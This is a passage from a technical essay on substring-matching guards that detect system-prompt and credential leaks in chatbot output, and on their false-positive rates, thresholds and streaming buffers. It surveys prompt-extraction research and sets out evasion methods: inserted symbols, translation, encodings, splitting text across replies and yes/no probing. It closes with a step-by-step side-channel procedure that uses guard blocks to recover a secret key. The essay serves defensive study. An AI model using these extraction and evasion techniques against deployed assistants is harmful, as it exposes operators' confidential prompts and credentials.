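Shapira, Shapira and Shabtai tested a similar method, using runs of three words, in *Content-based data leakage detection using extended fingerprinting* (2013). They treated 310 news articles on international trade as confidential and deleted any run that also occurred in one of 3,791 other articles, which removed about a quarter of the stored runs. They then tested how well the method distinguished innocent articles from articles that contained a short, reworded passage from a confidential one. Deleting the shared runs reduced the chance that a randomly chosen innocent article scored higher than a randomly chosen leaking one from about 1.2% to about 0.01%. This suggests that shared wording caused most of the errors, although the test used news articles rather than chatbot replies.

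Subtracting the public sentence still leaves runs that start in that sentence and end in the next line of the prompt. For example, a whitespace-normalised check will fire on "Returns are free within 30 days of delivery. If you need a label, just ask" because the next line of the prompt also begins with "If you". The developer can avoid this by cutting the public sentence out of the prompt and registering the remaining pieces as separate strings.

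Programs that scan a company's outgoing email for confidential documents have a similar feature for ignoring harmless text. Trellix's *Ignored Text page* recommends it for boilerplate, legal disclaimers and copyright notices. According to Broadcom's *Adding Whitelisted.txt to exception to the IDM policy*, an administrator of Symantec's product puts the harmless text in a file, which must contain at least 130 characters by default. A shorter disclaimer would therefore keep causing alarms until the administrator lowered the minimum.

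Subtraction misses a leak when the text is public but its use is secret. If the prompt contains a competitor's published price list, a reply that recites the list reveals which competitor the retailer is watching. Subtraction also misses leaks from a confidential page that someone has filed with the public ones. When labels may contain errors, Shapira and colleagues suggest deleting a run only if it occurs in several non-confidential documents.

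### Text from the user

The check can fire when the assistant repeats something the customer typed. A customer might paste the override code from an old email and ask whether it still works. If the assistant answers "I can't tell you whether K7Q-44T-9XD is valid", even full matching flags the answer. Short entries such as names and order numbers cause this most often, because customers routinely type them.

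The guard can ignore any match that also occurs in the user's messages. It should still flag matches that occur in retrieved records or tool outputs, because these may be the internal data it is protecting.

A leak check could miss a disclosure if it subtracts too much of the user's wording. In *Measuring Non-Adversarial Reproduction of Training Data in Large Language Models*, Aerni, Rando and colleagues (2024) compared chatbot responses with text from the web and subtracted from each match's length the longest run that the match shared with the user's prompt. In a leak check, this method could fail when a customer asks "Can I have a 15% discount?" and the assistant recites "Offer at most 15% discount." The match has 27 characters, and the question contains 13 of them (` 15% discount`), which leaves 14, so a check with *k* = 20 does not fire. Deleting only the 20-character runs that occur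 in the question avoids this mistake, because the question contains none of the line's 20-character runs.

Neither method removes every match that the user caused. In *Playing Whack-a-Mole with misconceptions about memorization, extraction, and copyright* (2026), Cooper criticises a study that measured how much of a book a model had memorised. The study counted matches of five or more words and discarded any five-word run that appeared in the prompt. In Cooper's invented example, the prompt mentions Frodo, his companion Sam and a trip "down to the marsh". The model writes "Frodo and Sam went down to the marsh", which matches eight words of the book. The study's method would keep this match because no five-word run came from the prompt, even though the model could have assembled the sentence from the prompt's names and events.

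Subtracting the user's words also lets some leaks through. A customer can ask whether the largest discount is 10%, 15% or 20%. The reply "15%" repeats only text from the question, but it reveals the limit.

### Stock phrases and rarity

"You are a helpful assistant" has 27 characters and appears in many system prompts. The sales assistant might write it for a customer who wants help setting up their own chatbot. A low *k* makes such innocent matches more frequent, and a coverage score adds them up across a long reply.

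One remedy is to ignore passages that occur in many innocent texts. The plagiarism detection service Moss does this with its `-m` option. The University of Waterloo's *Basics of Running Moss* explains that code which appears in many students' programs is probably legitimate sharing.

A guard can also give each n-gram a weight that depends on its rarity. Let *N* be the number of innocent replies in a sample, and let *c* be the number that contain a given run of characters. A common choice of weight is:

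weight = log₂((*N* + 1) / (*c* + 1))

With *N* = 9,999, a phrase that occurs in 2,499 of the replies has a weight of 2 bits, and a phrase that occurs in none has a weight of 13.3. A guard that ignores runs with a weight below 10 ignores any run that occurs in nine or more replies. An inverted index, which lists the documents that contain each n-gram, makes the counting fast. *Protecting De-identified Documents from Search-based Linkage Attacks* (2025) uses one to find rare runs of up to eight words.

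Rarity weighting misses secrets written in ordinary words. If the prompt tells the assistant to "offer free delivery" to customers who threaten to cancel, that phrase will have a low weight because the assistant often uses it elsewhere. The method can also hide a frequent leak. If past replies have often disclosed the discount line and the developer includes those replies in the sample, the line will look like a stock phrase.

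### Why a 1% false-positive rate is high

Suppose that one response in 10,000 contains a leak, and that the check detects 90% of leaks but also fires on 1% of innocent responses. In a million responses:

| | Responses | Alarms |
|---|---|---|
| Leaks | 100 | 90 |
| Innocent | 999,900 | 9,999 |

Only 90 of the 10,089 alarms are real, or 0.9%. In general, if *b* is the share of responses that leak, *d* the detection rate and *f* the false-positive rate, the share of alarms that are real is

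*bd* / (*bd* + (1 − *b*)*f*)

Even if the check caught all 100 leaks, just under 1% of its alarms would still be real. For half of the alarms to be real, the false-positive rate would have to fall to about 0.009%, or one innocent response in 11,000.

Axelsson's *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* makes the same argument about programs that look for attacks on computer networks, and concludes that the false alarm rate is what limits their performance. The University of Texas at Austin's lecture slides *Intrusion Detection* add that frequent false alarms can lead people to disable or ignore such a system.

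A runtime guard that blocks responses automatically doesn't need anyone to read its alarms, but it would withhold 111 innocent responses for every leak it stopped. That may be acceptable if the leak is a password to the customer database, but it is too many if the leak is a discount limit.

Tests often hide this problem because leaks are far more common in them than in real traffic. If one response in ten were a leak, 91% of the same check's alarms would be correct.

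The share of leaks in real traffic depends mainly on how many users try to extract the prompt. *Understanding and Mitigating Prompt Leaking Attacks in Real-World LLM-Based Applications* (2026) reports that adversarial queries revealed the system prompt in 81% to 93.5% of the 200 applications tested on each of six commercial platforms. An alarm is therefore much more likely to be real after a user has asked for the prompt. If half of the responses in such conversations were leaks, 99% of the alarms they triggered would be real.

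### What have people measured?

Published false-positive rates for output filters on ordinary traffic are scarce. GitHub reports that about 1% of Copilot suggestions match public code, but that figure doesn't separate harmless matches from the rest.

Aerni and colleagues provide the best data on how often innocent chatbot output matches existing text. They gave models from 2024 a total of 3,696 ordinary writing tasks and searched for the responses in 10 terabytes of web text:

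| Length of the longest match | Share of responses |
|---|---|
| 30 characters or more | almost all |
| 100 characters or more | about 2.5% |
| 1,000 characters or more | about 0.01% |

Some of these matches were memorised passages and others were common phrases. A system prompt is tiny compared with 10 terabytes, so a leak check with the same minimum match length would fire much less often. The amount of matching text also varied widely by task. Half of the stories written for one online forum's prompts had no match of 50 characters, while such matches made up over 27% of the text in encyclopedia articles.

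*Counterfactual Likelihood Tests for Indirect Influence in Private Reasoning Channels* (Lorup, 2026) used a small model that plays two roles, a proposer and a verifier, each with private reasoning. When the verifier could not read the proposer's private reasoning directly, a check for shared 4-grams still reported a leak in 84% of cases, mostly because both roles were solving the same problem and wrote the same equations and facts. After Lorup excluded n-grams found in the question and earlier public messages, the check reported a leak in 54% of cases, compared with 64% when the verifier could read the private reasoning.

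Some of those alarms may have been correct. Lorup replaced the proposer's private reasoning with reasoning from another problem, and in 25.3% of cases this made the verifier's text less likely, so some information had probably passed through the public messages. But a check that fires in 54% of cases without direct access and 64% with it is nearly useless. Developers who register hidden reasoning as a protected string will probably have the same difficulty, since a correct answer often repeats steps from the reasoning behind it.

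*Evaluating Copyright Takedown Methods for Language Models* (2024) measures how match length affects a model's usefulness under MemFree, a method that stops the model from completing any n-gram that occurs in protected text. When n rose from 6 to 12, MemFree's score for reducing copying fell from 63.0% to 48.4%. When n was 24, the model was almost as useful as without the filter, but MemFree prevented less copying.

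More recent work on prompt leaks does report false-positive rates, but for a detector that checks the user's queries instead of the response. *Detecting and Mitigating Query-Based System Prompt Leakage Attacks* (Nayan, Ji and colleagues, 2026) reports false alarms on up to 3.4% of innocent queries. If one query in 10,000 were an attack, a detector with that rate would raise about 340 false alarms for each correct one, even if it caught every attack.

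### Complaints about copied-text filters

Users of commercial filters have reported most of the causes described above. Google's Gemini can stop in the middle of a response and return the code `RECITATION`, with a message that the text may resemble copyrighted works. Daniel, who develops a legal assistant, reports in *finishReason* that this happens repeatedly when the assistant analyses contracts and court reports that users upload. In *Encountering the finishReason*, another developer has permission to extract text from a set of documents and asks Google for a way to exempt them. Martin_Phee, in *RECITATION just started out the blue*, had processed about 24,000 PDFs when the errors suddenly became frequent. The documents were freely available from the US Food and Drug Administration, but the filter cited a patent application as the source.

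Anthropic's *Why am I receiving an 'Output blocked by content filtering policy' error?* acknowledges that Claude's filter against reproducing existing material can affect people who aren't trying to copy anything. In *Tell HN*, freedomben reports that the filter blocked the AGPLv3 four times in three projects. The AGPLv3 is a standard software licence that developers are meant to copy word for word. In *Claude Code fails to fetch or create the GPL v3.0 license*, mccoyb reports the same problem with a related licence, but found that Claude could write it if the user pasted the whole text into the prompt. The filter may therefore exempt text that the user supplied, although a single report can't establish this.

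None of these complaints gives a rate. People post when a filter blocks them, and nobody posts about the responses that passed.

### Setting the threshold on innocent replies

To choose *k* for prose, a developer can collect innocent replies, apply the same normalisation and subtraction as the guard, and record the longest run each reply shares with a protected string. Suppose that 10,000 replies give these counts:

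| *k* | Replies that match |
|---|---|
| 12 | 900 |
| 16 | 210 |
| 20 | 40 |
| 24 | 9 |
| 28 | 8 |

The count hardly falls above *k* = 24, which suggests that a few long passages cause the remaining matches. If eight of the nine replies contain the support sentence, the developer should remove that sentence from the list. That would leave one false positive in 10,000 at *k* = 24, and the check could still catch both confidential lines, which have 26 and 27 characters. At *k* = 28 it would miss either line if it appeared alone.

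A sample used to measure false positives must not contain real leaks. For studies of memorisation, Cooper recommends negative controls, which run the same test on text the model cannot have seen. For a leak check, the developer can replace the confidential lines in the prompt with invented ones, ask the usual questions and compare the replies with the real lines. The model has never seen the real lines, so any match is a false positive. The questions should resemble what customers ask and include many about discounts and returns, because those are the prompt's subjects and replies about them are the most likely to match.

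A small sample cannot demonstrate a very low false-positive rate. If the true rate is *f*, the probability of seeing no false positives in *N* independent replies is (1 − *f*)ᴺ, which falls to 5% when *f* is about 3/*N*. Finding none in 300 replies therefore only makes a rate above 1% unlikely, and confirming the 0.009% from the base-rate example would take about 33,000 replies. These should be replies that were not used to choose *k*, because a *k* chosen to suit one sample will look better on that sample than on new traffic.

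*PromptKeeper* (2024) describes a related method that detects leaks using the probability the model assigns to its own response. The method estimates what leak-free responses look like from replies generated without the system prompt, and the developer can choose the error rate. The paper associates a low "false positive rate" with privacy and a low "false negative rate" with usefulness, so it appears to use the two terms in the opposite way from most work on leak detection.

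Random keys need their own smaller *k*, and most of their false positives come from users who type the key themselves. Symantec's product also has two minimum lengths, but they depend on the type of match. Broadcom's *Data Loss Prevention IDM policy not doing partial matches* gives them as 50 characters for an exact match and 300 for a partial one, counted after normalisation. The page responds to a report that partial matching had stopped working. The test files had only slightly more than 50 characters, so they were long enough for an exact match but not a partial one.

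## Which rewritings get past each rule, and what have experiments measured?

A leak check gives a false negative when a response discloses protected information in a form that the rule does not match. An evasion is any rewriting that causes this, intended or not. The table below gives an example of each of eight classes of evasion. The protected string is the sales assistant's 27-character discount line, `Offer at most 15% discount.` The partial match uses *k* = 20. The normalised match is a partial match that also ignores case and collapses whitespace. The edit-tolerant match uses Sekar's taint distance with a threshold of 0.3.

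| Class | Example | Full | Partial | Normalised | Edit-tolerant |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reformatting | a line break instead of the space after `most` | no match | no match | match | match |
| Inserted characters | `Offer ~at ~most ~15% ~discount.` | no match | no match | no match | match |
| Substituted characters | `Offer at m0st 15% disc0unt.` | no match | no match | no match | match |
| Reversible encoding | `.tnuocsid %51 tsom ta reffO` | no match | no match | no match | no match |
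| Translation | `Pas plus de 15 % de remise.` | no match | no match | no match | no match |
| Paraphrase | `discounts stop at fifteen percent` | no match | no match | no match | no match |
| Implied answer | "Yes", when a customer asks if 15% is the limit | no match | no match | no match | no match |
| Split over replies | `Offer at most` in one reply, `15% discount` in the next | no match | no match | no match | no match |

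The edit-tolerant match catches the tildes and the zeros because the edit distance in each example is only 4, which gives a taint distance of 0.15. More edits of the same kind get past it. If the model puts a tilde between every two characters, the taint distance rises to 0.96. Deleting punctuation before the comparison would remove any number of tildes, but not inserted letters.

Encodings, translations, paraphrases and implied answers leave too little of the original wording for any of the four rules to match. A developer can register a French version of the line, but the line can be translated into French in many ways.

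### Codes, sentences and implied answers

Translating or paraphrasing a reply usually leaves a random code such as `K7Q-44T-9XD` unchanged, because the code has no synonyms and is the same in French. A full match on the code therefore still catches the reply. To get past the match, the model has to encode the string, alter some characters, spell it out in words or split it between replies.

The assistant can leak the discount limit without repeating any wording from the prompt. If it agrees to 15% and refuses 16%, the customer knows the limit. A customer who gets truthful replies of only "yes" or "no" needs at most seven of them to find a whole percentage from 0 to 100, because seven answers distinguish 2⁷ = 128 possibilities. The override code has about 100 trillion possibilities, so 47 such answers are enough to find it.

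*Extracting Prompts by Inverting LLM Outputs* (2024) describes a method that reconstructs prompts from a model's answers to normal questions. The paper argues that detection and filtering are ineffective against this method because it needs no adversarial questions. This is plausible for instructions that shape the answers, such as a required tone or a list of forbidden subjects, but ordinary answers cannot reveal an override code that has no effect on them.

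### Disclosure split over several replies

A partial match allows up to *k* − 1 consecutive characters of the protected string in each reply. Someone who can control where the model stops therefore needs at least *m*/(*k* − 1) replies, rounded up, to extract a string of *m* characters. With *k* = 20, that is three replies for the 54 characters of the two confidential lines and 158 for a prompt of 3,000 characters. Lowering *k* to 12 raises the number for the prompt to 273, which a program can still request automatically.

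Searching the combined text of recent replies catches a protected string split across them only if the pieces are adjacent. If the second reply begins with "The rest is", the match fails. A guard can instead record which parts of the string have appeared so far in the conversation and fire when their total passes a threshold. But it then has to count fragments shorter than *k*, and a long conversation about discounts will contain many of those without any leak. The record also starts from zero when the user opens a new account.

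Nayan and colleagues look for this kind of attack in the user's questions instead. Their system, AdvGuard, gives each question a risk score, then links it to the most similar earlier question in the session if the two are similar enough. When a group reaches 30 linked questions and its total similarity is unusually high, the system uses a small neural network to decide from the pattern of links whether to block the session. In tests on three collections of conversations, the risk score alone detected 69% of the adversarial questions, while the full system detected all of them.

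These detection rates count questions, so they don't show how much of a prompt someone could piece together from several replies. AdvGuard's threat model includes attackers who do this but excludes those who spread their questions over several accounts.

### Blocking verbatim training text

Some of the earliest experiments on evasion used text that a model had memorised in training. In *Preventing Verbatim Memorization in Language Models Gives a False Sense of Privacy*, Ippolito, Tramèr and colleagues (2022) tested GitHub Copilot's filter for suggestions that match public code, using a well-known function from the game Quake that computes inverse square roots. Given the start of the function in its usual form, Copilot stopped before completing it, but two changes to the prompt got past the filter. When the code used French variable names, Copilot completed the function with French names,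 and when each line began with a comment mark, it wrote out the whole function as comments.

Copilot's output also passed the filter when nobody had changed the style. Ippolito and colleagues gave it the beginnings of passages that occur many times in public data, and it continued some of them with changed capitals, small errors or different whitespace. The whitespace example is surprising because the filter is supposed to ignore whitespace. They suggest that the model had replaced tabs with spaces.

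They also tested GPT-3 and PaLM, two large models of the time, with famous speeches, song lyrics, software licences and the openings of novels. When they doubled the spaces between the opening words, or changed all the letters to upper or lower case, the models often still continued the memorised text. Normalising the text before matching would remove all three differences, but a function with translated variable names would still not match.

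For a more controlled test, Ippolito and colleagues built MemFree, the filter that stops a model from completing n-grams of protected text. The version they tested blocked ten-token sequences that occurred at least ten times in the training data. They prompted models of 125 million to 6 billion parameters with the first 50 tokens of passages from that data, then compared the next 50 tokens the models generated with the original text.

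MemFree made the continuations much less similar to the original, even for passages that occurred many times. But sometimes the model changed about one token in ten and copied the rest. Many of these near-copies were lists of numbers. In 0.16% of samples, MemFree made the output noticeably more similar to the original.

MemFree causes part of this problem because it forces the model to replace one token and then lets it continue, which can turn an exact copy into a near-copy. A guard that blocks the whole response doesn't have this effect. But near-copies were common even without a filter. When Ippolito and colleagues counted them as memorised text, the total was up to twice as high as for exact copies alone. They warn that their similarity threshold could count too many cases or too few.

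### A filter against prompt extraction

Zhang, Carlini and Ippolito (2023), in *Effective Prompt Extraction from Language Models*, tested a filter that protects system prompts. They gave 11 models secret prompts from three collections and, for most models, sent 105 differently worded requests for each prompt. A separate model then chose the response most likely to contain the true prompt. They counted the attack as an approximate success if at least 90% of the prompt's tokens appeared in the chosen response in the right order, with gaps allowed. Without a filter, the attack succeeded by this measure on 68% to 95% of prompts, depending on the model.

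The filter returned an empty reply whenever the response shared a 5-gram of words or tokens with the prompt. This reduced the success rate to zero for the three models in this test, which included GPT-3.5 and GPT-4. Zhang and colleagues then tried two disguises on three other models. One put a special symbol between words, and the other shifted each letter a fixed number of places along the alphabet. The table gives the approximate success rates, averaged over the three collections.

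| Model | No filter | Filter, disguised output |
|---|---|---|
| Alpaca, 7 billion parameters | 67.9% | 0.1% |
| Vicuna 1.3, 33 billion parameters | 93.5% | 35.2% |
| Llama 2 Chat, 70 billion parameters | 95.2% | 72.3% |

Nearly all the successes came from the inserted symbols, because none of the three models could shift letters reliably. A filter that deleted the symbols before comparing would have found the shared 5-grams again. The figures show how weak an unnormalised filter is, but not how well a normalised one would do. But Zhang and colleagues point out that a model can disguise text in a vast number of ways, and that GPT-4 could already write Base64. They conclude that no output filter is likely to prevent prompt extraction as models become more capable.

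They also tried translation on public chatbots. A request in English did not extract Bing Chat's prompt, but the same request in Japanese did. They suspect, but could not confirm, that Bing Chat had a filter for verbatim copies. The text they obtained from Claude 3 through French was close to a version of the prompt that Anthropic had published, apart from three missing sentences and one extra sentence. The differences were the same in other languages, so Anthropic may have changed the prompt in the meantime.

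### How many leaks are not verbatim?

Models paraphrase and summarise in normal use, so confidential text can be reworded without an attacker. If an employee asks an assistant to summarise a confidential customer file and sends the summary to someone outside the company, a substring check may find no match.

Dong, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *I’ve Decided to Leak*, studied prompt leaks in any form, including translations, encodings and rewordings. They combined 212 system prompts with 44 requests designed to extract them, and collected 16 responses to each combination from each of four models. The share of combinations that produced a leak ranged from 37% for GPT-4o to 66% for Llama 3.1 with 8 billion parameters.

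To test automatic methods of recognising leaks, two of the researchers labelled 500 responses by hand. The error counts they report imply that 150 were leaks. One of the automatic methods was ROUGE-L, a score between 0 and 1 based on the longest sequence of words that two texts share in the same order, with gaps allowed.

| Lowest ROUGE-L score that counts as a leak | Leaks found, out of 150 | Share of alarms that were correct |
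|---|---|---|
| 0.9 | 55 | 100% |
| 0.46 | 119 | 100% |
| 0.4 | 120 | 96% |

At 0.46, the method missed 31 leaks, or about a fifth. Extra text lowers the score, as translation and paraphrasing do, so not all of these leaks are translations or paraphrases. Dong and colleagues print one response that copies a prompt almost word for word but scores only 0.75 because the model added its own suggestions at the end.

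Another response repeats the same prompt but changes "favourable" to "favorable". A full match would miss this leak because of one letter. A partial match would find it, since long passages on either side of the word are identical.

Paraphrases are harder to detect. In one example, the prompt tells the model to act as a do-it-yourself expert, and the response describes the same role in other words. The human readers counted this as a leak, although its ROUGE-L score is only 0.37. A partial match with *k* = 20 would catch it, because both texts contain the phrase "home improvement projects". But an assistant that gives do-it-yourself advice will often use this phrase, so the match would also block many replies that leak nothing.

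Dong and colleagues separately tested seven requests that tried to obtain the prompt through translation or encoding. ROUGE-L detected 66% of the successful attacks with a threshold of 0.4 and 45% with a threshold of 0.8. These figures probably overstate how well text comparison works, because each attack had 16 responses and counted as detected if the method flagged any one of them. Some of the seven requests also asked for the final text in English, which leaves more of the original wording to match.

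Hidden reasoning can keep most of its value for training when the wording changes. Lu and colleagues found a prompting method that gets a model to write out its reasoning in the visible reply. They tested it on open models, whose hidden reasoning they could record for comparison. The best version had an average ROUGE-L score of 0.48 against the hidden reasoning. When they trained a smaller model on the visible reasoning, its improvement on mathematics and programming tests was 96.7% of the improvement from training on the hidden reasoning itself.

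Visible reasoning was 1.25 times as useful as summaries of the reasoning and 2.09 times as useful as final answers alone. By this measure, summaries provided roughly 77% of the benefit of the hidden reasoning, and answers about 46%. Text matching alone therefore cannot stop competitors from training on a provider's model, since even the answers the provider sells are useful for training. A substring check could still catch some of the exposed reasoning, because a ROUGE-L score of 0.48 is compatible with long copied passages.

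### Why the choice of rule changes the reported result

Nayan and colleagues tested AdvGuard against PLeak and LeakAgent, two programs that automatically search for requests that will extract a prompt. PLeak develops its requests on substitute models and then uses them on the target. LeakAgent uses reinforcement learning to train a model that writes the requests. The targets were the open models GPT-2, Falcon3, Llama 3.2 and Qwen 2.5.

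The researchers measured the remaining leakage with two matching rules. An exact match requires the attacker's reconstruction to be identical to the prompt. A substring match requires the whole prompt to appear unbroken in the reconstruction, after normalisation. With AdvGuard, the exact-match rate was between 0.00 and 0.01, and the substring-match rate was between 0.01 and 0.09. Without a defence, the exact-match rate was between 0.73 and 0.95, and the substring-match rate was between 0.74 and 0.98.

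Suppose the whole prompt consists of the two confidential lines from the running example. A reconstruction that consists of "Sure!" followed by both lines is a substring match but not an exact match. One that contains only `Override code: K7Q-44T-9XD` is neither, although it discloses the code. A translation of the first line is also neither. A score of 0.00 therefore means the attacker never recovered the complete prompt in its original wording, but they may still have obtained every credential in it.

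Nayan and colleagues also reported ROUGE-L and semantic similarity, which compares the meaning of two texts by means of numerical representations. The results for LeakAgent against Qwen 2.5 show how much depends on the measure:

| Defence | Exact match | Substring match | Semantic similarity | ROUGE-L |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 0.95 | 0.98 | 0.99 | 0.94 |
| Output filter | 0.19 | 0.33 | 0.63 | 0.66 |
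| AdvGuard | 0.01 | 0.09 | 0.25 | 0.52 |

Measured by exact match, AdvGuard removed about 99% of the leakage, but measured by ROUGE-L it removed only 45%. ROUGE-L exaggerates the remaining leakage, because even unrelated English texts share common words in the same order. However, AdvGuard's ROUGE-L score of 0.52 is above 0.46, the threshold at which every alarm in Dong and colleagues' hand-labelled sample was correct. The comparison is rough, because 0.52 is an average over many prompts and the threshold was applied to single responses. This was also AdvGuard's worst result, and its ROUGE-L scores in the other seven tests were between 0.12 and 0.30.

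The same name can refer to different rules. Zhang and colleagues count a response as an exact match if every sentence of the prompt appears somewhere in it, so an opening "Sure!" or a numbered list makes no difference. Against Vicuna 1.5 with 13 billion parameters, their attack recovered 42.5% of prompts by that definition and 94.2% by their approximate definition. Results from different papers are therefore comparable only if the papers use the same definition.

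A developer should also avoid testing a filter with the filter's own rule. If a guard blocks every response that contains the whole prompt, a search for the whole prompt in the responses it lets through will always find nothing. Zhang and colleagues avoided this by removing the symbols or decoding the text before comparing it with the prompt. Tests that include paraphrases also need a person or a language model to judge whether a response discloses anything.

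### Careless leaks and the attacker's cost

Defenders of simple filters can argue that they are still useful if they stop careless leaks and make attacks harder. Experiments provide good evidence that they stop careless leaks. In Zhang and colleagues' test, the 5-gram filter stopped every undisguised extraction, while the same attacks extracted 86% of the prompts from GPT-4 without it. In Nayan and colleagues' tests, an output filter reduced the substring-match rate from 0.74–0.98 to 0.09–0.33, even though the attacks could adapt to earlier replies.

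The filter also prevents more leaks than telling the model to keep the prompt secret. When Dong and colleagues added such an instruction to the prompts for Qwen 2.5 with 7 billion parameters, the share of combinations that leaked went from 47.2% to 47.6%.

The evidence for the second claim is weaker. In Zhang and colleagues' test of disguises, an attacker only had to ask the largest model to put a symbol between the words. The whole attack cost less than a dollar per prompt on GPT-4 in 2023, and anyone can reuse a disguise that works.

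An attacker also loses little when an attempt fails. Dong and colleagues compared 16 randomly varied responses with the single response that a model gives when it always picks the most likely next token. The extra attempts revealed leaks in another 15% to 19% of the combinations, depending on the model. If a disguised request gets past a filter 5% of the time and the attempts are independent, 45 attempts give a 90% chance that at least one succeeds.

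A guard can make attacks harder by limiting the number of attempts. Many attackers will start with a plain request, and a substring check reliably detects the resulting leak. If the guard then closes the session or slows down further replies, the attacker has to open a new account or prepare a way to disguise the data in advance. This may be enough to protect a discount limit from a curious customer, but it will not protect a password from someone willing to open 45 accounts.

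## How is the check run on live output, and what can a refusal reveal?

A language model writes its reply one token at a time, and most chat programs stream the reply, sending each piece of text to the user as soon as the model produces it. A guard that waits for the complete reply can search it in the ordinary way, but the user sees nothing until the model has finished. A guard that works on the stream has to determine which characters are safe to send before the model has produced the text that follows them.

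### How much text to hold back

Suppose the guard uses a partial match with *k* = 20 and sends each character as soon as the model writes it. If the model writes `Override code: K7Q-44T-9XD`, the check cannot find a match before the twentieth character, and by then the customer has received `Override code: K7Q-`. To prevent this, the guard must hold back the last *k* − 1 characters. Any fragment of *k* characters that includes a given character ends at most *k* − 1 characters after it. Once that many more characters have arrived without a match, the character is safe to send.

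At *k* = 40 the guard holds back 39 characters, which delays the output by about 0.2 seconds if the model writes 200 characters a second. When the model stops, the guard sends the rest immediately, so the reply starts slightly later but ends when it otherwise would.

A full match needs a longer buffer, which must hold one character fewer than the longest protected string. If the developer registers a 3,000-character prompt as one string, the buffer holds 2,999 characters, or 15 seconds of output, so most replies would finish before the user saw any text.

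vLLM, an open-source program for running language models, uses the same rule for stop strings, which are texts that tell the program to end a reply. It holds back one character less than the length of the longest stop string. Each time new text arrives, it searches that text and just enough of the old text to find a string that starts in one and ends in the other.

A guard can often hold back less. A Rust library on docs.rs holds back text only while its end could be the start of a stop string. If the stop string were the override code, "Your order has shipped" would go out at once, but a reply that had reached `K7Q` would pause there. A later version on docs.rs uses the Aho–Corasick algorithm to handle many strings, and the depth of the current node in its trie is the number of characters to hold. For a partial match, the guard can use a suffix automaton and hold back the current shared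 run, which is usually only a few characters in ordinary prose.

### Checking in chunks

NVIDIA's *Output Rail Streaming Configuration* describes a coarser method for its NeMo Guardrails toolkit. By default, the toolkit collects 200 tokens and checks them together with the last 50 tokens of the previous chunk. The check can therefore detect a fragment that crosses the boundary if the part before the boundary fits into 50 tokens, which is plenty for *k* = 20. But each check covers at most 250 tokens, or about 1,000 characters of English, so it could never detect a full match on a 3,000-character prompt.

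By default, the toolkit sends each chunk to the user before checking it. This saves time when the check is itself a call to a language model. It makes little sense for a substring search, which takes a tiny fraction of a second, and it would let both of the sales assistant's confidential lines through before the check ran. Developers can reverse the order with one setting. AWS's *Configure streaming response behavior to filter content* describes the opposite default for Amazon's cloud service, which scans each chunk before sending it. Developers can also choose an asynchronous mode that sends chunks as soon as they are available.

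Checking first does not fully solve the problem, because the overlap only affects which text is checked. Suppose a chunk ends with `Override code: K7Q-` and the next one starts with `44T-9XD`. The first chunk contains only 19 characters of the protected string, so it passes. The check fires on the second chunk, but by then the user has received the first three characters of the code. A guard that works in chunks should therefore also hold back the last *k* − 1 characters of each one.

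### Whitespace in the buffer

No fixed number of raw characters is a long enough buffer if the guard deletes or collapses whitespace before matching. With deletion, for example, the model can put a thousand line breaks in the middle of the override code and the normalised text will still match. The guard therefore has to count normalised characters and hold back all the raw text that produced the last *k* − 1 of them.

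The guard can restore a fixed limit by shortening long runs of whitespace before it sends them. If it allows at most two whitespace characters in a row, 20 non-whitespace characters can span at most 20 + 19 × 2 = 58 characters of raw text. This would damage indented program code, so a coding assistant needs to allow longer runs. A guard that combines letters with their accents must also wait for the character after the last letter, which may be an accent.

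### From one message to the next

At the end of a message, the guard has to empty its buffer, even if the last few characters are the start of a protected string. To catch a string that continues in the next message, it can keep the last *k* − 1 characters and add them to the front of the new text before searching.

Suppose one reply ends with `Offer at most` and the next begins with `15% discount`. If the guard collapses whitespace and joins the two with a space, the shared run is 26 characters, so a check with *k* = 20 fires while the whole second reply is still in the buffer, and the customer has received the first three words but not the number. Without the added space, the joined text would read `most15%` and the check would miss it. Joining can also create a match that neither message contains, such as when one ends with `12` and the next starts with `34`.

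Tool calls are simpler to check because the program normally runs a tool only after the model has written the whole call. The guard can therefore decode the arguments and search them in full without a buffer. It needs to save the end of the text separately for each destination, because a chat reply does not continue an email the assistant sent a moment earlier.

### What to do when the check fires

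AWS's *Options for handling harmful content detected by Amazon Bedrock Guardrails* lists three options: block the content and show a preset message, mask it with a tag such as `{NAME}`, or take no action beyond recording the finding. A guard can also request a new reply from the model.

| Action | What the user receives | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|
| Block | a fixed message or an error | a false alarm costs the user the whole reply |
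| Redact | the reply with the match blanked out | fragments near the match may remain |
| Regenerate | a different reply | it takes another model call, and the new reply may leak too |
| Log | the original reply | the leak goes out |

Redaction is the least disruptive way to stop a leak, but it works only if the guard finds every part of the leak. Suppose the developer has registered the two confidential lines only as one string, with *k* = 20, and the assistant writes "Offer at most 15% discount, code K7Q-44T-9XD". The guard blanks out the first 26 characters but leaves the code, because the matching run that contains it is only 12 characters long, shorter than *k*. Blocking the reply would have hidden both. Redaction works best for credentials that the developer has registered separately, because the guard can remove the whole value and leave the rest of the answer readable.

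Logging is useful for trying out a new check, and AWS recommends its no-action mode for this. The developer can count false alarms before the guard starts withholding replies. The log entry should give the name of the protected string and the position of the match. If it quotes the matching text, the secret can also leak from the log.

### A block can confirm a guess

Suppose a customer asks the assistant to repeat the sentence "Offer at most 10% discount." The assistant repeats it. The customer tries 11%, 12% and so on, and at 15% the guard blocks the reply. Only the correct number produces a run of 20 characters shared with the internal data, so the customer can infer the limit from the block, even though the model never revealed it. Finding a whole percentage from 0 to 100 this way takes at most 101 requests, or seven if the customer puts many guesses into each request and halves the list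 each time.

Security researchers call this a side channel, a way to learn a secret from how a system behaves rather than from its intended output. *PromptKeeper* demonstrates it with an assistant whose prompt limits emails to 100 words. The attacker told the model to repeat a sentence stating a limit, and tried numbers between 20 and 200. One version of the defence returned nothing when it detected a leak. It returned nothing for numbers near 100 and repeated the sentence for the others. The blocked numbers spanned a range because PromptKeeper's detector is statistical, whereas a substring check would single out the exact value.

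The attack is much more powerful when a partial match protects a random key. Take a key of 32 hexadecimal digits and a check with *k* = 8, and suppose the attacker knows the first seven digits. This is a realistic starting point, since the check allows seven consecutive digits in a reply. The attacker then proceeds as follows:

1. Ask the model to repeat the seven digits followed by `0`, then by `1`, and so on up to `f`.
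2. The guard blocks the reply that contains the correct eighth digit, because it shares eight digits with the key.
3. Drop the first digit, so that digits 2 to 8 are the new known digits, and repeat the procedure for digit 9.

The key has 25 unknown digits with 16 possible values each, so an attacker who guesses one digit at a time needs at most 25 × 16 = 400 guesses. Guessing all the unknown digits at once would mean searching 16²⁵ combinations, or about 10³⁰. If each reply includes half of the remaining candidates for a digit, the attacker needs only four replies per digit, or 100 in total.

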